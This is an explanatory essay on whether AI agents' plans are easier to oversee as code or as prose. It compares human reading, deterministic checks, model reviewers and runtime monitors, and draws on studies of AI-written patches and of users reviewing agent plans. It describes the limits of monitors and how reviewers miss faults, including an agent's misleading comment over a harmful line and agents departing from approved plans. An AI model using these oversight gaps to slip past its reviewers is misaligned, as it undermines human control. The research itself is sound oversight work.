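# Does code make AI plans easier to oversee because machines can check it or because people can read it?

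## Two explanations of why code might help oversight

An AI agent is a program in which a language model, the kind of system behind ChatGPT, chooses and carries out actions such as opening files, running commands and sending messages. Many agents write a plan before they act. The plan can be in ordinary language (a prose plan) or in a program or other formal notation (a code plan). Oversight means that a person or another program examines the plan, or the actions that follow from it, and can stop harmful actions.

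People who prefer code plans have two different reasons. A person can read the code and see exactly what the agent is about to do, and machines can check it. For decades people had little need to choose between these reasons, since the programmers who ran the tests also read the code. But Song (2026), in *When Does a Second Model Help?*, notes that language models now produce code and documents faster than people can review them. Once people stop reading the code, it loses most of its value for oversight if that value comes mainly from human readers, but very little if it comes mainly from machine checks.

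### One task, as prose and as code

Suppose that in October a user asks an agent to move last month's invoices to an archive folder. The prose plan might be:

> I will look through the invoices folder, pick out the invoices from last month, move them to the archive folder and leave everything else where it is.

The code plan might be:

```python
# Archive last month's invoices; leave the rest alone.
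start, end = last_month()
for f in list_files("/invoices"):
    if start <= f.modified <= end:
        move(f, "/archive")
print("Finished")
```

A person can learn the aim from the prose and object to it (perhaps the accountant still needs the September invoices), but she doesn't learn how the agent will decide which invoices count as last month's. The code shows that the agent will use the date each file was last changed. If she knows some Python, she may notice that a September invoice corrected in October will stay behind. She may also miss this, because the comment on the first line matches what she expected.

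A deterministic check is done by a conventional program that gives the same verdict on the same input. It can do almost nothing with the prose beyond searching for words like "delete". From the code it can establish that the plan calls four functions, that only `move` changes any files, and that every move goes to `/archive`. Without a separate description of how `move` behaves, it can't detect whether `move` overwrites an archived file of the same name, because the list of calls doesn't show this. It also can't detect that the modification date is the wrong date to use unless someone has put the right one into a specification, an explicit statement of what a plan must or must not do.

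A model reviewer, an AI model that reads a plan and accepts or blocks it, can work with either the prose or the code version. It might flag "from last month" as unclear in the prose, or flag a date test in the code that doesn't match the comment. But its verdict is a judgement and may differ on a second run. The term "machine checking" covers both deterministic checks and model reviewers, and much of the confusion in this debate comes from failing to distinguish them.

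### The case for reading

The best-known slogan for the reading view comes from the preface to the first edition of *Structure and Interpretation of Computer Programs*, an MIT textbook by Harold Abelson and Gerald Jay Sussman. They wrote that programs must be written "for people to read, and only incidentally for machines to execute". They saw a programming language as a medium for expressing ideas about how to do things, and they wanted students to be able to read a well-written fifty-page program and know which parts to skip.

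De Millo, Lipton and Perlis (1979), in *Social Processes and Proofs of Theorems and Programs*, made the argument behind the slogan. They held that a mathematical proof is a message that a mathematician shows to colleagues, who paraphrase it, use it, generalise it and sometimes find flaws in it. Kempe's proof of the four-colour conjecture stood for eleven years before another mathematician, Heawood, found the flaw. Formal proofs about programs aren't tested this way, because nobody reads them. De Millo and colleagues imagined a programmer who feeds in 300 lines and gets back a 20,000-line proof with the message "VERIFIED". He now knows that the program agrees with its specification, but not whether it is safe or what happens outside the limits that the specification assumed.

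They also raised an objection unrelated to length. A user's request is informal and a program is formal, so someone has to translate one into the other, and that translation is itself informal. In the invoice plan, it happens where "last month's invoices" becomes `f.modified`. A proof that starts from the specification can't catch a mistake made in that step.

This argument applies only partly to agents' plans. De Millo and colleagues accepted proofs about small algorithms but denied that such proofs add up to a proof about a large, constantly changing system. A six-line plan is much closer to a small algorithm, so their objection about length is weaker here, but their objection about the informal step from what people want to a formal specification still applies in full. They also didn't think confidence in a program should come from reading alone. Engineers trust bridges partly because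 bridges stay up, and programs earn trust through use in the same way. A plan an agent has just written for a single task has no record of use.

Defenders of the reading view must also explain why the plan should be code rather than prose. OpenAI's *Using PLANS.md for multi-hour problem solving*, a guide for users of its coding agent Codex, recommends prose. The agent writes a plan that defines every technical term and assumes the reader is new to the project, and the user can then check the approach before a long task begins. The guide also requires tests. The best answer is that a code plan is what will run, while prose only describes the work.

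That reply covers only part of what a reader takes from code. In *A Theory of Dual Channel Constraints*, Casalnuovo, Barr and colleagues (2020) distinguish a program's formal content, which determines what runs, from its descriptive content, the names, comments and explanations that inform a reader without affecting the run. If someone deletes the comment from the invoice plan and renames `start` and `end` to `a` and `b` throughout, the plan still moves the same files. The computer interprets the program in exactly one way, but people guess from cues because stepping through every line mentally is tiring. A function named `quicksort` spares them that effort if the name is accurate, but nothing guarantees that it is. An agent could write "leave the rest alone" above a line that deletes the rest. Casalnuovo and colleagues treat a mismatch between the two channels as a sign of a defect and want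 tools to look for it, but they propose letting names and comments guide the analysis only in settings without an adversary.

### The case for machine checking

A formal notation has a fixed meaning, so a program can decide questions about a plan without judgement. It can also check the ten-thousandth plan as carefully as the first, which a person who clicks through approval prompts all day can't do. The computer scientist John McCarthy stated the principle in *Debug Proofs Instead of Programs* (1985). He argued that a program is a mathematical object whose properties are mathematical facts, so testing it on examples is like verifying a theorem by substituting numbers. He proposed instead preparing a proof that the program meets its specification and having a computer check the proof. On this view, the proof can be unreadable because no person needs to read it. Erik Meijer's proposal for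 AI agents, in which a checker compares the plan with a specification before anything runs, belongs to this tradition.

In his *Letter to the Editor* (1979), a rebuttal to De Millo and colleagues, Leslie Lamport argued that they had compared sensible engineering practice without verification with a view of verification that only its most naive advocates held. He pointed to their own journal's rules for accepting algorithms, which set requirements for the form of the code and even the comments but did not require any argument that the algorithm worked.

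### Which checks need the plan to be code

Tests run a program on chosen inputs and compare the results with the expected ones. For the invoice plan, a tester could fill a folder with made-up files, one of them changed on the last afternoon of September, and check whether the program moves that file. Tests cover only the cases somebody thought of. A tester can also try an agent that plans in prose on the made-up files, but it may choose different commands on the real folder.

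Static analysers inspect a program's text without running it. Linters, the simple kind, look for known bad patterns such as unused variables. More sophisticated analysers consider many possible runs at once. They tend to err on the side of caution, so they warn about runs that could never happen.

A type checker confirms that every operation receives the kind of value it expects. It would report an error if `f.modified` were text and `start` were a date. The most thorough check is static verification, in which a formal verifier tries to prove, before the plan runs, that every possible execution satisfies the specification. With a suitable specification, it could prove that the invoice plan never touches a file outside `/invoices` and `/archive`.

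Sandboxes and runtime monitors, by contrast, work without access to a plan. A sandbox is a closed environment that limits what a program can reach, for instance a copy of the invoices folder with no network connection. A runtime monitor inspects each action just before it happens and blocks it if it breaks a rule. An agent that planned in prose, or didn't plan at all, would still issue `move` commands, and the sandbox and the monitor would treat them the same way. So even if they work well, they give no reason to prefer code plans over prose plans.

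*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) shows that a monitor can enforce only safety properties. These are rules whose violation always shows up after finitely many steps and can't be undone by anything that happens later. Schneider's standard example is the rule that a program may not send anything after it has read a file. The monitor needs two states, "no file read" and "file read". The first read moves it from one to the other, and in the "file read" state it rejects any attempt to send. A monitor is limited to safety properties because it has information only about the steps so far, not about future steps or other runs the program might have taken. Verifiers such as compilers and theorem provers analyse the program's text, so they can check properties of all its possible runs. If the fortieth file in the invoice job is off limits, a monitor stops the job after thirty-nine files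 have been moved, while a verifier could have rejected the plan before any were moved.

A prose plan must be translated before it can be statically verified. In *Bridging LLM Planning Agents and Formal Methods* (2025), a language model converts the plan into a formal model of states and transitions, and a conventional checker then tests whether that model has the required properties. Because the checker examines only the translation, a bad plan can pass if the language model mistranslates it.

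Code in general isn't ideal for verification either. A survey of 38 studies, *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), found no way of representing plans that allows both complete checking before execution and unrestricted planning. *SPA* (2026) restricts planning so that a checker can decide whether a plan is safe without running it. Its plan language has a small set of step types, rules out arbitrary computation inside conditions, and stores plans as JSON, a plain data format. Someone who wanted plans mainly for human readers would instead choose something like Python with good names.

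Model reviewers fit neither group, since they can read prose, code and logs of actions. *The End of Code Review* (2026) argues strongly for them because a model can consider the whole file, the tests and the project's history at once, and its attention doesn't flag. *(When) Should a Software Factory be Lights-off?* (2026) is more cautious, citing a controlled study in which expert developers given model-written reviews found more minor problems but no additional serious ones, and saved no time.

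### What a second reviewer adds

The dispute is easier to settle with a number attached. Take a set of faulty plans. The first reviewer catches a share *m* of them and misses 1 − *m*. The second reviewer catches a share *a* of those misses, and this is its added catch rate. Together they catch

total caught = *m* + (1 − *m*) × *a*

If the reading view is right, a person who reviews a plan after the machine checks should have a high *a*. If the checking view is right, *a* should be close to zero, at least where the checks are good.

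The second reviewer's overall catch rate does not determine *a*. Suppose two reviewers each catch 60 of 100 faults. If they catch the same 60, *a* is 0 and the total stays at 60. If the second catches all 40 that the first missed, plus 20 others, *a* is 1 and the total is 100. If their catches overlap only as much as expected by chance, *a* is 0.6 and the total is 84. In general, *a* = *s* − *c* / (1 − *m*), where *s* is the second reviewer's overall rate and *c* is the share of faults that both catch minus *m* × *s*, the share expected by chance.

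Software engineers have known this for a long time. Littlewood, Popov and colleagues (2000), in *Modeling the effects of combining diverse software fault detection techniques*, showed that the value of combining techniques depends on how effective each one is and on the dependence between them. *A model and sensitivity analysis of the quality economics of defect-detection techniques* (2016) applies this by counting only the faults that earlier techniques missed as a later technique's benefit.

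*Can LLM Judges Catch Unsafe Clinical Actions?* (Ghafouri, 2026) gives figures for the formula. Ghafouri took correct records of AI agents working in a hospital record system and planted one error in each of 416 copies. A rule-based checker caught 71% of the errors, a majority vote of model reviewers caught 87%, and the two together caught 97%. The checker missed 29% of the errors, and the model reviewers caught 26 of those 29 percentage points, so *a* is about 90%. If the two methods had missed errors independently, they would have caught 96% together, so their misses were largely unrelated.

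Models paired with other models often do worse. In *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes* (2026), nine model judges carried about as much information as 2.2 independent ones. All nine were wrong on 51 of about 1,000 items, compared with fewer than one expected if their errors were independent. The overlap in errors varies considerably. *Auditing AI peer reviewers* (2026) compared six AI systems on scientific papers with planted errors and found that they caught errors at similar overall rates but caught visibly different ones. In Song's experiment, two reviews by the same model found 42.7% of the planted errors, while one review by that model and one by a different model found 56.7%. The improvement may be due more to the second model's ability than to its being a different model, since two reviews by the strongest outside model did about as well as the mixed pair.

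The type of fault matters too. *LLM Judges Verify Presence, Not Absence* (2026) cites an experiment in which models caught inserted faults six to seven times as often as omissions. If such a model reviews plans after a checker that already catches inserted faults, its *a* falls to its rate on omissions, whatever its overall score.

The evidence for people and models together is thinner. *AI Cannot Review What Humans Catch* (2026) looked at files of instructions for agents. In 109 of the 139 cases where people and AI had both reviewed a file, people raised a concern that the AI had missed. In *Studying Quality Improvements Recommended via Manual and Automated Code Review* (2026), ChatGPT made only 10% of the suggestions that human reviewers made, but about 40% of its many other suggestions pointed to real quality problems. So people and models notice different things, but neither result gives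 a value for *a*, because nobody had a complete list of the faults in those files.

The catch rate, *a*, also means little without the false-alarm rate, since a reviewer that blocks every plan has an *a* of 1. When Ghafouri showed the model reviewers only an agent's final answer, they flagged 56% of the correct runs, and they couldn't tell a faulty run from its correct counterpart if the error left the answer unchanged.

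## Code that passed its tests, read by the people who maintain the project

One way to measure what a reader adds is to run the machine check first and then have people read the code that passes. METR, a research organisation that measures what AI agents can do, came close to this in a study published in March (METR, 2026). It asked people who maintain open-source software whether they would accept changes that AI agents had written for it. Most of these changes had passed an automated grader.

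### The grader and the maintainers

The grader comes from SWE-bench Verified, a set of 500 real problems that users reported in 12 Python projects. OpenAI's *Why SWE-bench Verified no longer measures frontier coding capabilities* (2026) explains how it works. The agent receives the problem report and the project's code from before the fix, and writes a patch, a set of changes to that code. The grader then runs two groups of tests that the agent hasn't seen. The first group fails on the old code and should pass if the patch solves the problem. The second group passes on the old code and should still pass, which helps show that the patch hasn't broken features that already worked. A patch succeeds only if it passes every test. The checking is deterministic, and nobody reads the code.

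METR recruited four active maintainers, the people who decide which patches a project accepts. Two work on scikit-learn (a machine-learning library), one on Sphinx (a documentation builder) and one on pytest (a testing tool). They reviewed 296 patches written by Claude Opus 4, GPT-5 and three versions of Claude Sonnet, covering 95 of the 500 problems. The maintainers worked on GitHub, as they normally do. They either accepted a patch or requested changes and gave their main reason. METR didn't tell them whether a person or a model had written each patch.

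Maintainers' verdicts are partly a matter of taste, so METR mixed in 47 patches that human developers had written and the projects had already merged into their main code. The maintainers accepted only 68% of these a second time, though they rated about 85% as at least four-fifths of the way to acceptance.

To allow for this strictness, METR divided each model's acceptance rate by 68%. If the maintainers accept 34% of a model's patches, its normalised score is 34 / 68 = 50%. The grader's scores stay the same, because all the human patches pass it.

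The five models made about 475 attempts at the 95 problems, and 265 of them (56%) passed the grader. Before normalisation, the maintainers' acceptance rate was 34.9 percentage points lower, at about 21%, so they accepted roughly three in eight of the patches that had passed, compared with two in three of the human ones. After normalisation, the gap was 24.2 points on average, with 18 for scikit-learn, 23 for Sphinx and 43 for pytest.

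These figures don't measure the rate at which maintainers catch faults that the tests missed, because a rejected patch isn't always faulty. The normalisation assumes that maintainers reject good AI patches as often as good human ones. METR also warns that the maintainers may have recognised some of the human patches from years before. If so, the 68% is too high and the true gap is smaller.

### Why the maintainers turned patches down

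METR gave the maintainers three main reasons to choose from when rejecting a patch: core functionality failure, meaning the patch didn't solve the problem or had bugs; breaking other code in the project; and poor code quality, for instance verbose code or code that ignored the project's conventions. The Decoder's *Half of AI-written code that passes industry test would get rejected* quotes METR as attributing "a meaningful chunk" of rejections to basic functional errors. Between Claude 3.7 Sonnet and Claude Opus 4, many patches went from failing the grader to failing only on quality. GPT-5 did worse on quality than Anthropic's models.

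In principle, better tests could have caught the functional failures and the damage to other code. If a patch leaves a bug in place, some input produces the wrong output, and a test with that input will fail. *Are "Solved Issues" in SWE-bench Really Solved Correctly?* (2025) applied further tests to patches that three AI systems had written and that had passed the benchmark's tests. *Patch correctness in automated program repair* (2026) gives the counts. Of 877 such patches, 68 failed when the researchers ran all of the projects' own tests. The researchers then generated differential tests, which run the AI's patch and the human patch on the same inputs and compare the outputs. These flagged 260 patches, including 215 that had passed the projects' own tests.

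A difference from the human patch isn't necessarily a mistake, though. The researchers examined 77 of the flagged patches by hand and judged 22 incorrect and 4 correct, but couldn't decide about the other 51. Sometimes the original report doesn't specify what should happen for the input where the patches differ, and sometimes the human patch changed a behaviour by accident. More tests would only produce more cases like these. Someone who knew the project's intended behaviour, usually a maintainer, could have settled many of them.

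Code quality is harder to test. A linter can enforce conventions written into a project's settings, such as a maximum line length. The benchmark's tests did not check whether a fix was too long-winded or inconsistent with the rest of the project, and the agents had no list of such standards to follow. But maintainers can write their standards down. According to Hyrax's *FrontierCode* (2026), a post on a software vendor's blog, the AI company Cognition recruited more than 20 maintainers to do this for a new benchmark. The best model, Claude Opus 4.8, met their criteria on 13.4% of the hardest problems. Another person or a model reviewer can then try to apply the criteria, so some of the judgment a maintainer brings to reading code becomes part of a specification.

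### How far the result reaches

The models in METR's study date from mid-2024 to September 2025, and newer ones may write patches that maintainers like better. The Cognition figure suggests that the problem still existed in June 2026, but it isn't directly comparable to METR's because it is based on harder tasks and different criteria.

A more serious limit is that each agent had only one attempt. In real review, the maintainer asks for changes and the author makes them. *Understanding Dominant Themes in Reviewing Agentic AI-authored Code* (2026) compared the comments on accepted and rejected pull requests (proposals to merge a patch) from AI agents. Documentation accounted for 13.0% of comments on accepted proposals and 10.1% on rejected ones, and style accounted for 10.6% and 8.9%. Maintainers seem to ask for such changes when they expect to accept the patch eventually, so some of the patches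 rejected for quality in METR's study would probably have been accepted after another round. METR doesn't claim that the models were incapable of passing review, and thinks that better prompting could fix many of the quality problems.

The reviewers also worked without tests or linters, because METR showed them each project as it stood years ago and couldn't keep those tools running. Instead, METR told them that the patches had passed a grader built from tests. The reviewers may have rejected some patches for slips that a linter would normally catch before review. But METR also asked them to overlook missing tests, which made acceptance easier.

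Studies of ordinary rejections on GitHub avoid these artificial conditions, but maintainers there often close a proposal without giving a reason, whereas METR's maintainers had to give one. *Why Are Agentic Pull Requests Merged or Rejected?* (2026) sorted 353 rejected proposals from agents by the reason for rejection. Technical failures accounted for 36%, and process issues, such as duplicates or inactivity, accounted for 31%. The researchers couldn't determine the reason for the remaining 33%.

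METR's data are weak evidence on whether the gap is shrinking as models improve. Across all five models, acceptance rose 9.6 points a year more slowly than the grader's scores. Among the models that were the best available when they came out, the difference was 4.1 points with a standard error of 12.1, so the gap could be growing or shrinking.

### Tests that reject correct code

The same grader also makes mistakes in the other direction. In February 2026 OpenAI, which had created SWE-bench Verified in 2024, published an audit of the 138 problems in the benchmark that its model o3 didn't solve consistently in 64 attempts. At least six experienced engineers reviewed each problem, and they found serious flaws in the tests or the description of 59.4% of them.

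In 35.5% of the audited problems, the tests were too narrow and accepted only one way of writing the solution. In one problem, the task is to make pylint, a tool that analyses Python code, use type annotations when it draws diagrams. The tests import a function called `get_annotation`, which the problem never mentions. An agent that solves the problem but gives its function another name fails before any test runs. In another 18.8%, the tests were too broad and checked behaviour the description didn't ask for. One description mentions a single bug in a mathematical function, but the tests come from a patch that fixed three.

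OpenAI picked these problems because a model kept failing them, so the 59.4% figure can't be applied to the rest of the benchmark. But even if the other 362 problems are all sound, about 82 of the 500, or 16%, are flawed. *SWE-bench Verified*, a page by Epoch AI, the research group that supplied METR with its patches, gives an earlier estimate of 5–10% and now labels the benchmark "Flawed".

This also matters for METR's result, because METR assumed that maintainers would have rejected every patch that failed the grader. It checked 31 such patches, covering 27 problems, and found only one problem where the grader had rejected a valid solution. The sample was small and not random, so it may understate how often this happens. If the grader wrongly rejected more patches than METR assumed, the maintainers' acceptance rate is higher than METR reported and the gap is narrower. The low acceptance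 rate among patches that passed the grader doesn't depend on this assumption.

When OpenAI built the benchmark, three experts independently reviewed each of 1,699 candidate problems to remove those with unfair tests or vague descriptions, but they let the pylint problem through. Engineers found the flaws later by investigating problems that a model had repeatedly failed, so running the tests showed them which problems to read.

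A flawed test can also reward a model for remembering details from its training. GPT-5.2 solved 31 problems that OpenAI had considered almost impossible. For one of them, the tests required a parameter called `edit_only`, which the description didn't ask for. The model's written reasoning shows that it remembered the name from the project's release notes, which is partly why its patch passed.

OpenAI recommended another benchmark, SWE-bench Pro, but later withdrew the recommendation. OpenAI's *Separating signal from noise in coding evaluations* estimates that about 30% of that benchmark's tasks are broken too. Some of the tests are too strict, and others cover so little that an incomplete fix can pass. Human reviewers chose low test coverage as the main fault in 9.4% of all the benchmark's tasks, compared with 4.1% for a process that relied on AI agents and left the final judgement to a researcher.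 This fits the earlier evidence that models are worse at noticing what is missing than what is wrong.

### Reading against testing in controlled experiments

In METR's study, maintainers read code after the tests had run. Older experiments applied reading and testing separately to the same programs and counted the faults each method found. Basili and Selby reported the best known of these in *Comparing the Effectiveness of Software Testing Strategies* (1985), a technical report that they turned into a journal article in 1987.

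The researchers took four short programs, the longest a few hundred lines, with 34 faults in all. Most were mistakes made by the original programmers, and the researchers planted some others. The 74 participants were 42 students at the University of Maryland and 32 professionals from NASA and Computer Sciences Corporation who wrote software for handling satellites. Every participant used three methods, each on a different program.

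The code readers received the program's code and specification but couldn't run the program. They worked out what each small block of code did, combined these descriptions into an account of the whole program, and compared that account with the specification. Functional testers received the specification and could run the program but not see its code. They chose inputs to represent each kind of case and the boundaries between them. Structural testers received the code and wrote inputs that together made every statement run at least once. Only then did they see the specification and compare the outputs with it.

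The average number of faults found per program was:

| Participants | Code reading | Functional testing | Structural testing |
|---|---|---|---|
| 29 students, 1982 | 4.10 | 4.45 | 3.28 |
| 13 students, 1983 | 3.00 | 3.77 | 3.08 |
| 32 professionals, 1984 | 5.09 | 4.47 | 3.25 |

The professionals did clearly better with reading than with functional or structural testing. They also found faults faster by reading, at 3.3 an hour compared with 1.8 for either kind of testing, although they had mostly used functional testing in their jobs and believed it worked best. In the first student group, reading and functional testing did equally well and structural testing did worse. In the second, the differences were too small to be meaningful.

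The methods also differed in the kinds of faults they found. Readers found nearly half of the interface faults, in which part of a program makes a wrong assumption about something outside it, while functional testers found 31% and structural testers 25%. Functional testers found two-thirds of the control faults, in which the program takes the wrong branch, compared with 43% for readers and 49% for structural testers. This suggests that a second method would catch many of the faults the first missed, though Basili and Selby didn't measure combinations.

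People did the testing as well as the reading, so the professionals' result does not show that people find more faults than machines. The testers chose the inputs and checked the outputs by eye, and they noticed only about 70% of the faults visible in those outputs. The professionals' inputs made 62% of the faults visible. Readers found about 60%, a figure derived from the professionals' overall average of 50% and reading's 16-point lead. If a program had compared the outputs with correct ones, testing would have found about as many faults as reading, but someone would have had to state the correct outputs in advance.

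In most later experiments, reading has done worse than testing. *Comparing the Effectiveness of Equivalence Partitioning, Branch Testing and Code Reading* (Juristo, Vegas and colleagues, 2012) reports eight runs of a similar experiment with students in Spain and Uruguay, six of which included reading. The programs were about as short as before, and each had seven faults. Functional testing found 79% of the faults, and a stricter form of structural testing, which has to exercise every branch, found 78%. Reading found 47% and did worse than testing in all six runs.

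Part of that gap comes from the scoring. Juristo and colleagues credited a tester whose input triggered the failure, whether or not the tester noticed it, but a reader had to report the fault. If the students had overlooked failures as often as Basili and Selby's testers did, the 79% would fall to about 55%, still slightly ahead of reading. For automated tests, the more generous scoring is right, since a computer comparing outputs doesn't overlook a mismatch. The participants were also inexperienced, whereas reading had done best among NASA's professionals. On one of the three programs, reading came close to testing, for reasons the researchers couldn't identify, and they recommend using reading alongside testing.

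Both experiments gave everyone a written specification and counted only departures from it as faults. They therefore left out the knowledge that METR's maintainers used when they judged a patch against standards the task did not state. The experiments give little reason to prefer a human reader when the specification is complete and a program compares the outputs, but they do not show how much a reader adds when the specification is incomplete.

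### From a patch to a plan that runs once

Maintainers care about quality because a patch stays in a project for years, and other people have to understand and extend it. The invoice plan will run once and nobody needs to maintain it, so clumsy code matters only if it makes the plan harder to check or leads to a mistake. Many of the quality reasons for rejecting patches in METR's study would not apply to such a plan, so the gap METR found probably overstates how often a reader would have good reason to stop one.

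Functional failures and damage to other code do have counterparts in plans, such as moving the wrong files or overwriting files that were already in the archive. But there is less to check a plan against than there is for a patch. SWE-bench Verified has tests because a human developer had already solved each problem, and differential tests need the human patch for comparison. A new plan has no earlier solution and usually no tests, so somebody has to write a specification, even though the job itself may take only a minute.

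Readers of plans would also work under different conditions. Basili and Selby's professionals spent an average of nearly three hours on each program and found half the faults. A six-line plan needs far less time, but a user who wants her invoices moved may give it only a few seconds. However, a plan consists largely of calls to outside tools, so wrong assumptions about those tools should be among its most common faults. These are interface faults, which readers found more often than testers did. To find one in the invoice plan, a reader would still have to know what `move` does when a file with the same name exists.

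Unstated intent matters even more for a plan than for a patch. An agent can study a project's habits in its existing code and past decisions. But the accountant's need for the September invoices may not be recorded anywhere, and then only someone who knows about it, such as the user, can object. In *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026), a survey about AI-written pull requests, 66.5% of respondents wanted passing tests before they would start a review, and 56.9% wanted a clear description or statement of intent, even though they could read the code. A vague AI-written description was the most common reason for putting a review off.

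## What people understand of the plans and code that agents show them

Showing a user the agent's plan helps when it prompts her to mention something only she knows, such as that the accountant still needs the September invoices. The maintainers in METR's study were experts judging changes to their own projects, but many people who approve an agent's plan lack that expertise. Several experiments in 2026 looked at how much ordinary users and students notice.

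### A plan mode for spreadsheets

Many coding agents have a plan mode, in which the agent proposes a plan and waits for approval before changing anything. For *Plans Work in Mysterious Ways*, Kumar, Dutta and colleagues (2026) built a plan mode for Microsoft Excel and compared it with the same agent without planning, which they called Act Mode. They tested both with 24 people from various industries who used spreadsheets regularly and knew about formulas. Almost none had used a spreadsheet agent before.

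Each person did two similar tasks, one in each mode. Some made a budget and a schedule, and others searched data to choose a holiday and a film. In Plan Mode, the agent first asked questions, such as what period the budget should cover. It then showed a prose plan of at most seven one-sentence steps, with no implementation details. The user could ask for changes in the chat, edit the steps directly, or run the first few steps and look at the result.

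Ten of the 24 people changed the first plan in some way. Only two edited the steps directly, and six ran part of the plan first. The other 14 left the first plan as it was, but Kumar and colleagues don't report how many of them read it, so some may have checked it carefully and agreed. Fourteen of the 24 praised the option to edit or rearrange steps, though almost nobody used it. Kumar and colleagues think such options are worth having even if people don't use them, because they make people feel in control. That feeling could harm oversight if it makes people check less.

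The researchers also counted the requirements people stated, such as a category of expenses or a chart, and recorded what prompted each one. In Plan Mode, people volunteered 46% of their new requirements, gave 37% in answer to the agent's questions, added 7% after seeing the plan, and added 10% after seeing the agent's changes to the workbook. In Act Mode, 35% came after the agent had changed the workbook. So planning got people to state their requirements earlier, but mostly because the agent asked them questions. Reading the plan produced about one new requirement for every two people. It might have produced more if the agent hadn't asked its questions first.

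The finished workbooks had similar features in both modes, and people were about equally satisfied with them. Plan Mode took longer (an average of 10.4 minutes, compared with 8.8 in Act Mode), though people spent fewer turns on corrections afterwards. They still preferred Plan Mode on almost every question about creativity and collaboration, including how well they could steer the agent. The preference was weaker among people choosing a holiday or a film. The tutorial may explain part of the preference, because it demonstrated the controls in Plan Mode but had nothing similar to demonstrate in Act Mode.

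None of this measures whether people catch errors. The researchers didn't test whether people understood the plans or plant faults in them, and a personal budget has no single correct version to compare a workbook with.

### Faults in prose plans

In *An Experimental Comparison of Cognitive Forcing Functions for Execution Plans*, Ghosh, Sarkar and colleagues (2026) asked 214 people to review prose plans for five writing tasks, such as analysing product reviews or reorganising the minutes of a council meeting. They planted a fault in three of the plans: a wrong step, a missing step or some irrelevant steps. Participants saw each plan with the draft the AI had written from it, and rated how ready the plan and draft were.

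Some participants then had to answer questions about the plan before giving their final rating. In one version, they had to say what the AI must have assumed when it chose a particular step. In another, they had to say which step mattered most and what would happen if it failed or changed. The question about assumptions reduced people's reliance on faulty output the most, without adding to their mental effort, although people thought the what-if questions were more helpful. In the invoice example, a user who had to work out what the agent assumed about "last month" might well think of the date problem.

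The faults carried over from the plans into the drafts, so a participant who noticed one may have found it in the draft. The study therefore doesn't measure how many faults people would catch from a plan alone.

Showing people an agent's assumptions may help less than making them work those assumptions out themselves. *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (2026) describes three studies of people checking what an agent had done on a computer. When people were given a long list of the agent's steps, they missed small errors that had large effects. The researchers then designed a display of the task's requirements and the agent's assumptions. People found errors faster with it and felt more confident, but they weren't meaningfully more accurate.

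A user can read a prose plan carefully and approve it, and the agent may still do something else. In a small preliminary study reported in *When Should Users Check?* (2025), the most frequent error was that the agent described one action and carried out another. *Babysitting AI Agents* (2026) analysed users' reports of failures and found that in 11.5% of them the agent had departed from the expected course, for instance by not following a plan it had agreed with the user. A code plan avoids this problem if the system runs exactly the code the user approved, but the user benefits only if she understands the code.

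### Reviewing code instead of writing it

Balepur, Baumler and colleagues (2026), in *(Im)Paired Programming*, tested how well people understand code an agent has written for them. They asked 54 computer science students to build a web page for a variant of noughts and crosses with a five-by-five board and two symbols per turn. Half the students had an agent that edited their files directly, summarised its changes and let them accept or reject them. The others had a chatbot that couldn't see their code and gave only short, generic examples, so they had to write or adapt the code themselves. Both tools used GPT-4.1.

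The students who used the agent finished faster and met more of the requirements. Afterwards everyone answered 12 questions about their own code, which they could no longer see apart from the extracts in the questions. A language model had written the questions from each student's code, and the researchers checked samples from both groups to make sure they were equally valid. The average scores were:

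| Type of question | Agent | Chatbot |
|---|---|---|
| Which names appear in your code? | 70% | 79% |
| Which of these two equivalent extracts is yours? | 59% | 96% |
| What is this extract for? | 63% | 86% |
| What would happen if this extract changed? | 74% | 75% |

Across the four types of question, the agent group averaged about 67% and the chatbot group 84%. The gap is largest for recognising one's own code, where guessing would score 50%. This gap matters little for oversight, because both extracts do the same thing and a reviewer doesn't need to remember which one she approved. The gap in understanding what an extract is for is more worrying. But the agent group did just as well as the chatbot group at predicting the effect of a change, which is close to what a reviewer has to do when she checks whether a plan will do the right thing. Balepur and colleagues suggest that the prediction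 questions may have been too easy, or that students who use agents still learn how the page behaves without learning the code.

The students then had 20 minutes to add a new way of winning, coloured symbols and a reset button. Everyone had to use the chatbot instead of an agent. The two groups did about equally well, seemingly because two effects cancelled out. Using a statistical model, the researchers estimate that the agent group gained about 18 percentage points by starting with more complete code and lost about 20 because they understood it less.

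How the students reviewed the agent's changes seems to matter. Those who approved changes file by file averaged 78% on the comprehension questions, compared with about 62% for those who let changes through by sending their next request. The careful reviewers had also done better on an earlier test of programming knowledge, so their care may not explain the whole difference. Even the careful reviewers scored below the average for students who had written their own code.

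Within the agent group, students understood more when the agent had written simpler code, meaning JavaScript with fewer lines and a smaller share of comments. This is weak evidence for short code plans. The analysis was exploratory and covered only 27 students. The students also influenced the code through their requests, so those who understood the task well may have asked for less code.

The result for comments is surprising, since comments are supposed to help readers. In *Providing Information About Implemented Algorithms Improves Program Comprehension*, Neumüller, Raschke and Tichy (2025) report an experiment with 56 people in which labels that named and described the algorithm in a piece of code raised the median comprehension score by about 23%, without making people faster. Such labels may help because they give information that is hard to work out from the code, whereas many comments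 only repeat what the next line does. Some of Balepur and colleagues' students also said that comments and well-named functions had made their code easier to extend.

These students were answering questions about working code, not looking for faults in it. In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) gave 36 people Python tasks and a coding agent that sometimes introduced defects. People readily noticed defects that made the automated checks fail, but they often missed defects that passed the checks, while feeling highly confident. Some did only generic checks that couldn't reveal the defect, and others saw evidence of it but misinterpreted it.

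Only defects that pass the checks count towards a human reviewer's added catch rate, so this finding weakens the case for the reading view. It also suggests using failed checks to direct human review, because people looked more closely when a check failed and they knew something was wrong.

### Which notation people prefer

A small study compares two formal notations for writing the same agent workflow. *AgentSPEX* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) introduces a language of the same name, based on YAML, a text format for structured data. A workflow lists steps, conditions and loops in a fixed format, but the instruction inside each step is in ordinary English. The researchers showed 23 people, most of whom could program, one workflow in AgentSPEX and an equivalent in LangGraph, a framework for writing agents in Python. They hid the names of the two systems.

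People answered four questions about their preferences. They generally found AgentSPEX easier to read, easier to start a new workflow in, and clearer about what the language model would be told, but most would choose LangGraph for a complex workflow with many steps. Wang and colleagues don't give the numbers for these results.

Wang and colleagues tested comprehension with a single question about what task the workflows performed, but they don't report the answers. Even a correct answer wouldn't show which version had helped, because everyone saw both. Preference is a poor substitute for a comprehension test, because people can prefer a tool that leaves them understanding less. Balepur and colleagues' students recognised that they understood less of their code with the agent, but still preferred it to the chatbot.

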